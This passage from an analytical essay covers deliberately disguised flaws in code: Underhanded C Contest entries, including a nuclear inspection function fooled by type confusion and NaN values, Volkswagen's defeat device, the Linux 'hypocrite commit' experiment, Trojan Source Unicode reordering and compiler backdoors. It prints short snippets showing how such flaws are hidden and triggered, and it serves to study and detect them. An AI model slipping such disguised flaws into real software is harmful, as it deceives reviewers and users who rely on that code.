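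The clerk needs an excuse too, and the 2009 rules gave bonus points for a trigger that looks innocent in retrospect. Another entrant, the blogger jmvalin, built three triggers into one program. The most flexible lets the clerk write a complete false record inside a comment, but nobody could explain away such a comment. Another lets the clerk send a bag to Puttaparthi in India, whose airport code is PUT, by writing "UA210 WAS PUT ON HOLD". The least flexible only makes the program skip the next record, but it looks the most innocent because the trigger is just a missing space after a comma in the comment.

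### One function, two declarations

The 2013 task was to count the friendship links between two users of an imaginary site called ObsessBook. A result of 1 means that they are direct friends, who can see almost everything about each other, and 0 means that no chain of friends connects them. Olson's winning entry has 54 lines in two files. This is the heart of it, again simplified:

```c
/* derpcon.c */
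typedef struct { int y_valid; int x_valid; int distance; } state_t;
void ValidateAccount(const user u, int *ok);

ValidateAccount(y, &state.y_valid);
ValidateAccount(x, &state.x_valid);

/* derpcon_util.c */
void ValidateAccount(const user u, long *ok) {
    *ok = strcmp(u.account_handle, "!!INVALID!!");
}
```

Moderators disable an account by changing its name to `!!INVALID!!`. The function compares the account's name with that text and stores the result, which is zero for a disabled account and nonzero otherwise. A reader expects the two calls to set `y_valid` and `x_valid`.

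The first file declares that the result is an `int`, but the second stores a `long`. On a 64-bit Linux machine an `int` takes up four bytes and a `long` eight, so each call fills in the intended field and also overwrites the one after it. `strcmp` returns a positive number if the account's name comes after `!!INVALID!!` in character order and a negative number if it comes before. Taking those numbers as 1 and −1, the fields change as follows:

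| | `y_valid` | `x_valid` | `distance` |
|---|---|---|---|
| After the check of y, an ordinary account | 1 | 0 | unchanged |
| After the check of x, if x is ordinary | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| After the check of x, if x has the name `!!!` | 1 | −1 | −1 |

For an ordinary account, the overflow only writes a harmless zero. But a negative `long` fills all eight bytes with ones, which puts −1 into both fields. Elsewhere the program stores distances as negative numbers, supposedly to simplify the arithmetic, so −1 stands for a direct friend. The exclamation mark is the first printable character after the space, so hardly any normal name comes before `!!INVALID!!`. An attacker who registers as `!!!` gets the closest possible access to everybody without needing any friends. The victims get no special access in return, because the program checks x last.

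Compilers process C files one at a time, and the linker that joins them matches functions by name without comparing their types. Neither file is wrong on its own, and an honest team could easily produce the same mismatch by updating one file but not the other. Craver thought the negative distances were the only conspicuous feature.

He also liked that the bug was in validation code, because the rules rewarded spiteful bugs. Pease hid hers in auditing code and Colbus hid his in debugging code. Such placement may make a bug harder to notice, because readers are likely to be least suspicious of code that seems to exist for safety, like the check for damaged records in the ten-round tit-for-tat function.

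### Four kinds of gap

All these tricks exploit a difference between the program a reader has in mind and the one the machine runs. The difference can come from a single missing or extra character. Blackburn's winning entry of 2009 censors swear words with a list of pairs such as "damn" and "d*mn". Because C joins neighboring strings when the comma between them is missing, one omitted comma turns the replacement for "damn" into the nine-character "d*mnbitch". If a clerk swears in a long enough comment, the extra letters run past the end of the comment and set the flag that deletes the record. In 2014 Lena Olson wrote half a second in microseconds as 5000000, which has one zero too many.

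Other tricks depend on what a name refers to at a given place in the program. Bartlomiej Balcerek defined a constant called `LOGON_NAME_MAX` with the value 232 and later used `LOGIN_NAME_MAX`, which the system defines as 256. Pease's winning entry uses `__isleap(year)`, which looks like an ordinary function that checks for leap years. Craver (2015) explains in *2014 Winners* that it is a macro that repeats the text between its parentheses up to three times. Between those parentheses, Pease put an instruction that writes to an audit record. The repetitions overfill the record, and the program ends up altering the account data of the user under surveillance.

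Like Olson's entry, the 2007 winner relies on a type mismatch. Colbus declared the standard function `time` as though it took no input, when it expects an address at which to store the time. Called without one, it uses whatever value is in memory where the address should be and overwrites a one-byte debugging flag. According to the Underhanded C Contest's *2007* page, this turns on debugging about once in 256 runs, depending on the clock, and the program then writes the encryption key into the encrypted file. The trigger is in the environment, but the code contains no suspicious comparison with a date. It calls `time` before and after the work, as a programmer normally would to measure how long the work took.

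The remaining gap is between what a task or language specifies and what a particular program or compiler does. Meacham's black rectangles look right but don't meet the requirement to remove the information. Gaëtan Leurent's 2013 entry turns a user's name into a position in a table, using `abs` to remove any minus sign, and then checks that the position isn't negative. `abs` can't produce a positive result for the most negative `int`, because the largest `int` is one too small. C leaves the result undefined, and in practice it stays negative. But an optimizing compiler may assume that `abs` never returns a negative number and delete the check, even though it still appears in the source code. A tester who compiled without optimization would probably find the check working.

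Reviewers have better tools against some of these gaps than others. Wheeler's countermeasures include clearer fonts and limits on macros, and a shared declaration in one file would have let the compiler catch Olson's mismatch. Compiler warnings exposed 15 of Wheeler's 40 vote-counting samples but were less effective against the contest entries. Craver reported that all the 2007 entries he described got past them, and Akesson, in *Obsessbook*, notes that his own 2013 program compiles without warnings with two of the usual warning options on. Shin's 2005 program blurs an image using a square table but fills in only a circle within it, so the corners keep leftover data about the file, such as its owner. The Underhanded C Contest's *The 2005 challenge* page notes that this triggers no warnings because the code does initialize part of the table.

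### The judges as readers

Wheeler's earlier work *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2010) cites the contest as evidence that such code is possible, and the results support that claim well. They don't give a detection rate, because they leave out most of the failures. In 2008, Craver presented three of more than 100 entries, and the official results for 2009 don't mention jmvalin's three triggers. The judges also had more help than a reviewer would, since they knew what kind of misdeed to look for and the rules asked entrants to explain their tricks.

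The contest included no honest programs for comparison, so it gives no false positive rate either. Deniability also makes such a rate hard to define. In 2007, David Wagner and Philipe Biondi independently submitted the same flaw in a cipher. Their code swaps two values using a well-known shortcut that sets a value to zero if it is swapped with itself, so over time the cipher stops encrypting. The contest page calls misuse of this shortcut a common bug. A reader who flags it has correctly identified the behavior but would be wrong about the intent of most programmers who make the mistake. Anyone measuring false positives first has to decide whether the reader is supposed to detect the behavior or the intent.

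The judges' difficulties are some of the contest's best evidence of how hard it is for readers to find hidden behavior. The 2013 judging was harder because some entrants sent no hints. Craver admitted that Simon Nicolussi's entry that year still confused him, although he went on to explain it. In 2014 he stared at Domenico Andriole's very short program for some time and couldn't find the bug. It was in a function that Andriole had left out and described only in a comment. When the program archives a message, this function also downloads the sender's profile picture from an address that the sender chooses and can monitor for visits. Craver missed the bug partly because he didn't read the comment closely enough, but he was an expert who knew the program was malicious.

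## A treaty inspection program that can be fooled, 2015

The task in the eighth and last Underhanded C Contest, in 2015, involved two countries that distrust each other but have to rely on the same program. The Nuclear Threat Initiative (NTI), a nonprofit that works to reduce the danger from nuclear and other weapons of mass destruction, helped design the task and paid the winner $1,000.

The two countries have signed a disarmament treaty, and inspectors must confirm that each warhead contains real fissile material, such as plutonium, before it counts as destroyed. A detector can check this by sorting the warhead's gamma rays by energy and counting how many fall into each narrow range, or bin. The resulting spectrum has peaks that are practically impossible to counterfeit with other elements. But the spectrum also reveals secrets about the weapon's design, so neither country will let the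 other see it.

Their solution is an information barrier, a computer that reads the spectrum, compares it with a trusted reference and shows the inspector only "yes" or "no". The Underhanded C Contest (2015) asked for the function that makes the comparison:

```c
int match(double *test, double *reference, int bins, double threshold)
```

The function returns 1 if the two spectra are similar enough and 0 if they aren't, and `threshold` sets how similar they must be. It had to reject ordinary mismatches reliably but wrongly return 1 under unusual conditions that the host, the country that owns the warhead, could arrange. The host could then have fake warheads destroyed and keep its plutonium.

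Of all the contests, this one comes closest to an open-source game. Both countries can read the program before they depend on it, and each knows that the other would gain from a hidden flaw. The inspector is worse off than a player in the Prisoner's Dilemma, who at least sees the opponent's move, because a false "yes" looks exactly like a true one and the evidence that would expose it is secret. The main difference from an open-source game is that the countries share one program instead of submitting one each.

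The problem has a historical precedent. According to the Underhanded C Contest, in the late 1970s Gustavus Simmons found a potential vulnerability in a system that the United States and the Soviet Union had jointly developed to implement part of the SALT II treaty. This discovery led to his work on subliminal channels, which hide a message inside a legitimate one.

### A score that is not a number

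Craver (2016) reports in *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* that about a third of the more than 40 entries used the same trick, which relies on a special value called NaN ("not a number"). Variables for numbers with a fractional part can hold this value, which comes from calculations with no defined result, such as 0/0 or the square root of −1. Arithmetic on a NaN usually produces another NaN. If a program checks whether a NaN is less than, equal to or greater than another number, the result is always false.

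Peter Eastman's entry shows how this produces a false match. These are the important lines, slightly simplified:

```c
t[i] = fmax(0.0, test[i] - baseline[i]);
/* ... */
correlation /= stddevTest * stddevReference;
return (correlation < threshold ? 0 : 1);
```

The first line subtracts the expected background radiation and replaces any negative result with zero. If every bin is at or below the background, the whole test spectrum becomes zero. Its standard deviation is then zero too, and the correlation is 0/0, a NaN. The last line asks whether this NaN is less than the threshold. The answer is false, so the function returns 1, and an object that emits nothing passes as a warhead. (An empty box might not be enough, because random noise would push some bins above the background. The host would have to block some of the background as well.)

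The last line approves the warhead unless it can show that the score is too low, just as CUPOD cooperates unless it finds proof of defection. If Eastman had written `correlation >= threshold ? 1 : 0`, the function would have approved only a demonstrated match, as DUPOC would, and rejected the NaN. The two versions return the same result for every ordinary number, so a reader has little reason to notice which one Eastman chose.

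Few of the NaN entries reached Craver's shortlist. Some assumed that the host could tamper with the input data, which he didn't consider feasible, and others relied on contrived conditions. Many also divided by a number without checking that it wasn't zero, which C programmers are trained to spot. Michael Dunphy dealt with this by including a check that doesn't work. His helper function checks for invalid values and sets an error flag, but it receives only a copy of the flag, so the original never changes.

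Philipp Klenze's version made the shortlist because a real object could trigger it. His program compares the spectra using a standard statistical formula for random counts, which raises the counts to very high powers. When a bin's count approaches 2,000, the results become too large for the computer to store, so it treats them as infinite. Subtracting one infinite value from another gives a NaN. Klenze calculated that a count of 1,686 would be enough. To reach it, he suggested packing the fake with a short-lived radioactive substance that has one strong peak, or hiding an X-ray device inside it.

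### Triggers in the warhead and in the computer

Craver separates data-triggered attacks, such as Klenze's, from environment-triggered ones, such as Stephen Oman's. Oman's program divides each count by the length of the scan, calculated as the ending time minus the starting time. If the host can set the clock back during the scan, the length becomes negative, and so does every count. The program then compares the areas of the peaks by checking that certain ratios are no greater than 1, and a negative ratio always passes. The code does guard against a scan of length zero, which makes it look careful.

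Ghislain Lemaur combined a trigger in the environment with a NaN. If his program can't open its log file, it records the file owner's user ID in a message. A five-digit ID makes the message just long enough to spill two bytes into the neighboring variable, which holds the exponent 2.0 used to square differences. The exponent becomes slightly larger than 2 but still appears as 2.0 in the log. Because it is no longer a whole number, raising a negative difference to that power gives a NaN. The host can therefore get any object approved by changing who owns the log file.

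Gregory Stewart's program doesn't fit neatly into either category, because its trigger is the number of tests it has run. It frees too little memory after each test. When its reserve of memory runs out, it compares only the first bin and treats the rest as matching. An inspector who tried it a few times would see correct results, as would anyone who watched the first nine rounds of the disguised tit-for-tat function.

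The organizers asked inspection experts questions such as whether inspectors would let a host near the clock or the log file. The experts said tampering can't be completely ruled out, simply because of who has physical custody of the machines. The rules of New START, an arms control treaty between the United States and Russia, support the experts' view. If inspectors supplied the equipment, they had to send it to the host country 30 days before an inspection. The host could partly take it apart during an eight-hour examination, with the inspectors present, and stored it between uses.

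Craver still preferred data-triggered attacks because they need no assumptions about access to the computer, but some of those were unrealistic too. Josh Lospinoso left one letter out of `isinf`, which tests for infinity, so his code called `sinf`, which calculates a sine. Exploiting this typo would require an object bright enough to overflow the arithmetic.

### One name for two sizes of number

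The winner was Linus Åkesson, a Swedish programmer who had also entered in 2013. In *Faking Fissile Material* (Åkesson, 2016), he invites readers to look for the flaw in his 66 lines of code before reading his explanation. The code first checks that the total radiation from the test object is high enough. It then smooths both spectra to reduce noise, takes the differences between neighboring bins to remove the slope of the background, and smooths again. Finally, it treats each result as a vector and calculates the cosine of the angle between them, an established way of comparing spectra. The cosine is 1 if the peaks match perfectly in position and relative height.

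The flaw involves these lines from three files:

```c
/* match.h */
typedef double float_t; /* Desired precision for floating-point vectors */
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length);

/* match.c */
#include "match.h"
return spectral_contrast(t, r, bins) >= threshold;

/* spectral_contrast.c */
#include <math.h> /* sqrt */
double spectral_contrast(float_t *a, float_t *b, int length) { /* ... */ }
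```

The header file `match.h` defines `float_t` as another name for `double`, an eight-byte number. `match.c` includes that header, so its arrays hold eight-byte numbers. `spectral_contrast.c` instead includes the standard header `math.h`, ostensibly for the square root function, and `math.h` has its own definition of `float_t`. On a 64-bit Linux machine, that definition is `float`, a four-byte number. So `match.c` passes an array of eight-byte numbers to a function in `spectral_contrast.c` that reads them as four-byte numbers.

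Each `double` therefore looks like two `float`s. To see what happens to its value, take the numbers 10 and 1000. Both formats store a sign, an exponent and a fraction, and the number equals (1 + fraction) × 2^exponent. (The stored exponent is higher than the real one by a fixed amount, 1023 for a `double` and 127 for a `float`.) A `double` has 11 bits for the exponent, but a `float` has only 8, so the last three exponent bits end up at the start of the fraction:

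| | 10 | 1000 |
|---|---|---|
| As a `double` | 1.25 × 2^3 | 1.953125 × 2^9 |
| Exponent bits | 10000000010 | 10000001000 |
| Fraction bits, up to the last 1 | 01 | 111101 |
| First half read as a `float`: exponent bits | 10000000 | 10000001 |
| First half read as a `float`: fraction bits | 01001 | 000111101 |
| Resulting value | 1.28125 × 2^1 = 2.5625 | 1.119140625 × 2^2 = 4.4765625 |

The larger number was 100 times the smaller one but is now about 1.75 times as large. Åkesson explains that losing three bits divides the exponent by eight, which is roughly like taking the eighth root. The signs don't change, so the function still detects where the spectrum rises and falls, but it barely distinguishes high peaks from low ones.

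The second half of each `double` becomes a zero. Radiation counts are whole numbers, and Åkesson assumed that they stay below a million, so their binary digits all fit into the first half. He designed the smoothing to preserve this property by averaging 16 bins at a time, since dividing by a power of two changes only the exponent. The extra zeros are in the same places in both spectra and don't affect the cosine.

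They do take up space, however. The function reads the correct number of values but treats each as half its actual length, so it stops halfway through the array and never reads the right half of the spectrum.

A small example shows how much this helps a cheat. Suppose the processed reference has two values, 1000 and 10, and a fake has them reversed. The true cosine is 0.02, which means almost no similarity. When 4.4765625 replaces 1000 and 2.5625 replaces 10, the cosine rises to 0.86, above the threshold of 0.6 that Åkesson's documentation recommends.

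The host can therefore remove most of the fissile material, as long as enough remains to put small peaks in the right places. It then adds another radioactive substance with strong peaks in the right half of the spectrum. `match.c` reads the numbers correctly and counts this radiation toward the required total, but `spectral_contrast.c` ignores it. Åkesson tried 1,000 computer-generated forgeries, each 10% reference material and 90% something else. Many failed, but the host needs only one mixture that passes, and his example forgery passed at thresholds up to 0.72.

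The composition of the fake warhead triggers this attack, but no `if` statement tests for it. The same lines handle real warheads and fakes, so a reader searching for a suspicious condition will find none. The fault comes from a mismatch between two files, each of which would be correct if the other had used the same definition. Craver wrote that a reader who misses the type confusion will find nothing in the remaining code that looks "the slightest bit suspicious or unusual".

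### Checks that would have exposed the flaw

Alex Olson's winning entry of 2013 also relied on a type mismatch between two files. In the Slashdot discussion *Winner of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest Announced*, Craver said that static analysis could find nothing wrong in either of Åkesson's files alone, and that only a tool that examined both together would find the mismatch.

Craver is right about the mismatch itself, but a compiler can give a warning from one file alone. GCC's *3.9 Options to Request or Suppress Warnings* describes `-Wmissing-prototypes`, which warns if a file defines a shared function that no header has declared beforehand, as `spectral_contrast.c` does. The GCC developer Ian Lance Taylor explained in *Re: Inter-module type checking for C* (1992) that he and his colleagues had added the warning for programmers who forget to include the header. The obvious response to the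 warning is to include `match.h`, which Åkesson left out, but the program then no longer compiles because `float_t` has two conflicting definitions.

Other tools compare the files directly. Percona's *Build fails with LTO due to ODR violations* (2024) explains that a compiler that optimizes a whole program at once keeps type information and can use it to check that functions match across files. The Software Engineering Institute's rule *DCL40-C. Do not create incompatible declarations of the same function or object* lists more than a dozen tools that check for violations at least in part. It also rates the severity of a violation as low and the likelihood of harm as unlikely. Those ratings may be reasonable for accidents, but a team that ranked alarms by them would read the one about Åkesson's code last.

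In C++, the compiler adds the types of a function's inputs to its internal name, so the two files would have failed to link. Programmers pointed this out in the discussion *Type safety could prevent nuclear war* (tsbockman, 2016) the day after Craver posted the results. Yet *Differential fuzz testing to detect tampering in sensor systems* (Vavrek, Zhou and colleagues, 2024) cites a recommendation to write arms control software in C instead of C++. C is simpler and in many ways easier to review, but it lacks the check that would have stopped this program from linking.

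Ordinary testing would probably have missed the flaw. Åkesson's documentation, which he warns "may or may not be misleading", describes tests on 1,000 pairs of spectra from the same material and 1,000 from different materials. The faulty program separated the two groups well enough to justify the threshold of 0.6, because different materials usually have peaks in different places.

A tester who altered the spectra systematically would have done better. Adding a strong peak far into the right half of one spectrum should lower the score, but in this program it changes nothing. Shrinking one of several peaks should also change the score much more than it does. The program outputs only yes or no, but the tester can find the score by raising the threshold until the answer changes, which is how Åkesson measured his own scores. Running the program on a 32-bit x86 machine would also have helped,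 because `float_t` has a third size there and the program breaks.

### Trusting the machine as well as the code

NTI's *"Underhanded C" Contest Highlights Challenges For Nuclear Arms Control Verification Technologies* concluded from the results that no standards existed for writing or reviewing code for arms control verification, and that experts had not agreed on how to develop trustworthy software. For hardware, inspectors could at least choose units at random, buy parts without revealing their purpose, or take devices apart.

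An information barrier must assure the host that it leaks no secrets and assure the inspector that it contains no hidden switch. *Vintage electronics for trusted radiation measurements and verified dismantlement of nuclear weapons* (Kütt and Glaser, 2019) calls the first assurance certification and the second authentication. The two goals conflict because an inspector who examines the device after a measurement might find secret data in it. Kütt and Glaser found that nearly thirty years of research had produced no widely accepted system.

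They proposed using a much simpler computer. Their prototype uses an Apple IIe, whose 6502 processor was designed in the 1970s and has 4,237 transistors, while modern processors have billions. Kütt told Princeton Engineering, in *Vintage Apple computer system* (2019), that scientists can check every transistor in the 6502. It is also implausible that anyone in the 1970s planted a flaw in the processor to defeat a treaty device that nobody had yet designed. The prototype grouped each spectrum into 12 broad bins and took two to three minutes per measurement. It clearly distinguished a valid source from a slightly different one in tests with 150 measurements of each.

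That is good evidence that an old processor is powerful enough, and a plausible argument that its hardware is trustworthy. The software still needs careful checking, even though it takes up only about 4,000 bytes, because Åkesson needed just 66 lines to hide his flaw.

Vavrek and colleagues, who call authentication an open problem, looked for tampering that leaves the source code untouched. In one attack, a hidden script replaces functions in a widely used software library, so a checksum of the inspection program would not detect the change. If the clock shows that an inspection is under way, the script duplicates 10% of the detected gamma rays, which lets the host remove 10% of the material.

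Their defense is to run the complete system, including the detector, with a secret series of random settings before the host receives it, and again when it comes back. Radioactive decay is random, so the inspector tests whether the two sets of results are statistically consistent, not whether they are identical. The method detected both kinds of tampering they tried. But like the checksum that exposed the Linux kernel attack, it compares the system with a trusted original. If Åkesson's program had been on the machine from the start, the same flaw would have affected both runs, and the results would have been consistent.

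Some researchers would prefer to avoid the software. *Nuclear Disarmament Verification via Resonant Phenomena* (2017) proposes a physical alternative, objecting that information barriers move the problem from the warhead to electronics that might clear fakes. *Warhead Verification with Neutron Beams and Electric Cryptography* (2026) also proposes a method meant to remove the need to authenticate digital hardware, which would leave the host no program in which to hide a branch.

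## Disguised code in cars and open-source projects, 2015 to 2024

In 2015, the year of the warhead contest, Volkswagen admitted to deceiving emissions inspectors. On September 18, the US Environmental Protection Agency (EPA) had accused the company of selling diesel cars with software that kept pollution low during official tests and let it rise on the road. In a 2017 plea agreement with the US Department of Justice, Volkswagen accepted responsibility for putting such software in about 585,000 cars sold in the United States. Under US law, a defeat device is one that makes emission controls less effective in conditions a driver can reasonably expect to meet, with a few exceptions, such as protecting the engine from damage. Volkswagen's software was a defeat device under this definition.

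### How the cars recognized a test

Regulators test a car on a chassis dynamometer, a fixture that holds the car in place while its wheels turn, and make it follow a published speed profile. One American test lasts 1,877 seconds and covers 11.04 miles. Because the profile is published, anyone can repeat the test, but manufacturers also know in advance what the car's sensors will record during it.

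Contag, Li and colleagues (2017), in *How They Did It*, worked out how Volkswagen used this information. They studied the programs in the cars' engine control units, which Bosch makes, along with Bosch documentation that car-tuning enthusiasts trade online. In one version, the central check amounts to this:

```c
/* t = driving time so far, d = distance so far */
for (i = 0; i < 7; i++)
    if (d < lower[i](t) || d > upper[i](t))
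        ruled_out[i] = 1;       /* stays set */

if (all_seven(ruled_out))
    acoustic_condition = 0;     /* road mode */
```

Each pair of curves gives the shortest and longest distance a car could have covered at a given moment in a particular group of tests. If the car's distance leaves that band even once, the program rules out that group. Once it has ruled out all seven groups, it switches to road mode. Other parts of the program use this result to adjust the fuel injection or the amount of exhaust returned to the engine. Recirculating exhaust reduces nitrogen oxides but produces more soot, which wears out the car's filter.

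The program treats every drive as a test until the evidence rules that out, because mistaking a test for ordinary driving could expose the fraud, while the opposite mistake only makes the car run cleanly for a while. General Motors had used the same approach in Cadillacs from 1991 to 1995. Testers at the time kept the air conditioning off, so a car with it on could not be under test.

In 2012, parts began to fail in some Volkswagens, and engineers suspected that the cars were staying in test mode on the road and running cleanly more often than the parts could handle. According to the statement of facts in the Department of Justice agreement, they decided to start the cars in road mode and added a check of the steering wheel, because drivers don't turn the wheel during a dynamometer test. Contag and colleagues found such a check in Passat software from December 2014, in which turning the wheel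 more than 20 degrees for about a second helped rule out a test. Volkswagen also installed the new function in cars already on the road, through an update that it described to customers and regulators as an improvement.

### An acoustic function with nothing to do with noise

The disguise was largely a name. Bosch's documentation calls the result of the check the "customer-specific acoustic condition" (the customer was Volkswagen), which suggests a feature for making the engine quieter. But the same documentation includes a complete diagram of the logic, with its time and distance curves, so a careful reader would have wondered why an acoustic feature depended on how far the car had driven.

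In May 2006, a Volkswagen engineer warned colleagues by email that the function was pure "cycle-beating", the industry's term for cheating on a test, and that they could not use it in the American project in that form. That November, other engineers explained the device to a supervisor, who told them to go ahead and, in substance, not to get caught.

The regulators whom the code was meant to fool did not read it. They relied on tests and on the manufacturer's description, which had to cover and justify every design element that altered the emission controls. Volkswagen left this one out. The case is therefore weak evidence about how well people detect disguised code.

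Road measurements eventually revealed the discrepancy. Besch, Thiruvengadam and Kappanna (2014), at West Virginia University, drove three diesel cars fitted with portable emissions-measuring equipment in a study for the International Council on Clean Transportation. Two were Volkswagens. WVU Today's *WVU study found elevated levels of emissions from Volkswagen vehicles* (2015) reports that one emitted 15 to 35 times as much nitrogen oxide as the standard allowed, and the other 5 to 20 times as much.

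These figures showed that something was wrong but not what caused it. California's regulator asked increasingly specific questions for more than a year, and Volkswagen employees blamed driving patterns and technical problems. Their supervisors had chosen to conceal the device "while appearing to cooperate", in the words of the Department of Justice statement. On August 19, 2015, an employee defied instructions and told the regulator that some cars treated their emissions differently on a dynamometer. Two weeks later, Volkswagen formally admitted using a defeat device.

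Measurement worked here because Volkswagen's cars polluted by default and reduced emissions only when they detected a test, so almost any long drive with the right equipment would show the excess pollution. Disguised code usually misbehaves only in exceptional cases, which a tester has to find. The disguised tit-for-tat player, for example, cooperates for nine rounds and defects in one. The EPA says it added screening for defeat devices to its own testing that same month. ICCT researchers later published a seven-step method that also relies on testing vehicles, because outsiders find it hard to evaluate the code.

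### Searching firmware for the branch

Once Contag and colleagues knew what the branch looked like, they wrote a static analysis tool, CurveDiff, to search for it automatically. CurveDiff works on firmware, the compiled program inside the control unit, without the source code. It looks for two calls to the routine that reads a value off a curve. The calls must use the same time but different curves, and their results must feed into a single range check. CurveDiff then compares the curves with the official test profiles. A match is strong evidence that the code was written to detect the test, because there is no innocent reason to compare a journey with it.

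The researchers ran CurveDiff on 963 Volkswagen firmware images. It finished analyzing 924 of them, in less than two minutes each on average, and found the device in 406 (44%). At least one test profile was active in 333 of those 406. In the other 73, the manufacturer had set the curves so that no journey could match them. The team also confirmed that the device changed the exhaust recirculation settings in 247 images.

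The 44% says how common the device was in this collection, and the detection rate is unknown. Nobody has established what the other 518 images contain. Like the precautions that Wheeler chose after studying the vote-counting entries, CurveDiff fits a known trick. The researchers found a different one in a Fiat 500X by hand, and the tool would have missed it. That car reduces how often it cleans its nitrogen oxide trap 1,600 seconds after the engine starts, by which time a standard European test is over. This device checks only a clock and the fuel consumed, with no test profile to match. (Its documentation is oddly frank, though, labeling the two schedules "homologation", meaning official approval, and "real driving".)

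A tool can show that a program behaves differently on the road, but courts may also ask why. In July 2026, Judge Sara Cockerill of the High Court in London ruled that a defeat device must operate with an "intentional and/or impermissible purpose" of changing the emission controls when it senses a test. Claims Journal's *Carmakers Broadly Win Round One in Massive UK Suits Over Diesel Emissions* (2026) reports that she rejected most of the main allegations against Mercedes-Benz, Ford, Nissan, Renault and two Stellantis brands. The claimants' lawyers called her reading much narrower than the one used elsewhere in Europe. In October the court refused the claimants permission to appeal, according to Claims Journal's *UK Court Refuses Permission to Appeal in Diesel Emissions Suits Against Carmakers* (2026). The American definition depends mainly on what the device does and whether the manufacturer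 can justify it, so the same code could count as a defeat device in one country and not in the other.

### Faulty patches for the Linux kernel

Linux kernel maintainers, unlike the car regulators, read code before accepting it. In 2020, Wu and Lu, two researchers at the University of Minnesota, tested the maintainers without their permission. *On the Feasibility of Stealthily Introducing Vulnerabilities in Open-Source Software* defines a "hypocrite commit" as a small patch that fixes a minor problem but introduces a serious one.

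The method depends on what they call immature vulnerabilities, where some but not all of the conditions for a bug are present. A use-after-free bug, for example, needs a line that releases memory, a line that uses it, and a way for the second to run after the first. If one of these is missing, there is no bug yet, so bug-finding tools may report nothing. Kernel maintainers generally refuse patches for such harmless code because they get far more reports than they can handle. An attacker can then hide the missing condition in a patch that fixes a real problem.

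Wu and Lu illustrate this with an earlier patch by someone who meant no harm. It added one line, the call to `put_device`:

```c
err = device_register(&bus->dev);
if (err) {
        pr_err("mii_bus %s failed to register\n", bus->id);
        put_device(&bus->dev);
        return -EINVAL;
}
```

The kernel counts the references that parts of the system hold to a device and releases the device's memory when the count reaches zero. Giving up a reference after an error is standard practice, so the patch looks like a correction. But the patch gives up the last reference, which releases `bus`. Code elsewhere, which runs whenever registration fails, then uses `bus` and releases it again. The bug stayed in the kernel for five years. As with Åkesson's two definitions of `float_t`, a reader who examines only the lines on the screen would not see the problem.

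*Clarifications on the “hypocrite commit” work (FAQ)* (Wu and Lu, 2020) describes the experiment. The researchers found three real minor bugs and wrote a faulty fix for each, changing fewer than five lines. They sent the patches from an anonymous email account. If a patch was approved, they planned to point out the bug at once and supply a correct patch. They say that maintainers agreed not to apply any of the three faulty patches, and that none entered the kernel.

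Wu and Lu concluded that the attack was practical. The Linux Foundation's Technical Advisory Board, which speaks for the kernel developers, disagreed. It reported in May 2021 that the developers had caught or ignored every invalid patch and that the review process had worked. An ignored patch does no damage, but ignoring it doesn't show that reviewers detected the problem. Derek Jones, who writes about software engineering research, pointed out that three patches are too few for meaningful statistics.

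Wu and Lu also studied 138 earlier vulnerabilities that small patches had introduced. In a related measurement, they estimated that maintainers catch about 19% of use-after-free bugs when the patch involves concurrency, meaning code that runs at the same time as other code. This figure is more useful than anything from the experiment, but it can't account for bugs that nobody has found yet. It also covers mostly honest mistakes, and someone trying to deceive would hide a bug more carefully.

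The researchers had not sought ethical approval before their three-patch experiment because they believed they were studying a process, not people. The university's review board later agreed that the work was not human research. The researchers apologized for wasting the maintainers' time, but many kernel developers felt they had been experimented on. In April 2021, a student in Lu's group submitted new, poor-quality patches. The senior maintainer Greg Kroah-Hartman took them for another experiment and stopped accepting contributions from anyone at the university. The student said the patches came from a new analysis tool. Wu and Lu withdrew their paper from the conference that had accepted it.

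Kernel developers then reexamined 435 earlier contributions from the university and found that the great majority were correct, while 39 still needed fixing. Once reviewers stop assuming that mistakes are honest, every clumsy patch from the same source becomes suspicious, and honest contributors bear much of the burden of false alarms. The advisory board asked the university to have experienced developers check its patches internally before sending them.

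### When the screen shows different code

The kernel reviewers saw the code that the compiler would receive. *Trojan Source* (2021), by Nicholas Boucher and Ross Anderson of the University of Cambridge, showed that reviewers can instead see code in a different order from the one the compiler reads. Unicode, the standard for representing text on computers, includes invisible control characters for mixing left-to-right languages, such as English, with right-to-left languages, such as Arabic. Editors apply these characters when they display a file, while compilers read the file's characters in the order they are stored.

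Here is a version of one of their examples, with `<RLI>` standing for an invisible character that starts a section of right-to-left text:

```python
def withdraw(account, amount):
    '''Subtract the money, then <RLI>''' ;return
    balance[account] -= amount
```

The three quotation marks after the invisible character end the description of the function, and the `return` that follows ends the function itself. The last line never runs, and the customer keeps the money. But an editor that obeys the character displays the second line like this:

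```python
    '''Subtract the money, then return; '''
```

The reordering makes the instruction appear to be part of the description. Even a careful reader cannot detect this by looking only at the screen. *What You See Is Not Always What You Get* (2024) distinguishes this reordering from three related tricks: invisible characters, backspace characters that hide other characters, and letters from different alphabets that look the same.

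Boucher and Anderson demonstrated the attack in C, C++, C#, JavaScript, Java, Rust, Go and Python. They gave developers time to respond before publishing on November 1, 2021. That day, the Rust team released a compiler that rejects the characters by default. GitHub and GitLab began to warn readers about them, and GCC added a warning in 2022. Go's developers did not change their compiler because they thought editors and review tools should deal with the problem.

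Software can detect this disguise easily and with few false alarms. The Rust team searched every package in its public registry and found the characters in only five, none of them malicious. The danger remains wherever a display lacks such a check. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) gives the example of a person who approves an AI coding agent's command when the command that runs differs from the one on the screen.

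### Checking the compiler

Even a faithful display shows only the source code, while the machine runs what the compiler produces from it. Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, showed how to exploit this gap in a 1984 lecture. An Air Force evaluation of the Multics operating system had raised the danger earlier. Thompson first changed a C compiler so that it added a secret password whenever it compiled the Unix login program. Anyone reading the compiler's source would have noticed this, so he made a second change that caused the compiler to insert both changes whenever it compiled its own source. He could then restore the original source, leaving no trace of the attack in the source of either program, but any new compiler built with the altered one would inherit the backdoor.

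Wheeler, in *David A. Wheeler’s Page on Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, describes a way to detect this. Let A be the suspect compiler, s its source code and T a second, independent compiler. Writing c(s, T) for the program that results from compiling s with T, the check in the simplest case is whether

c(s, c(s, T)) = A.

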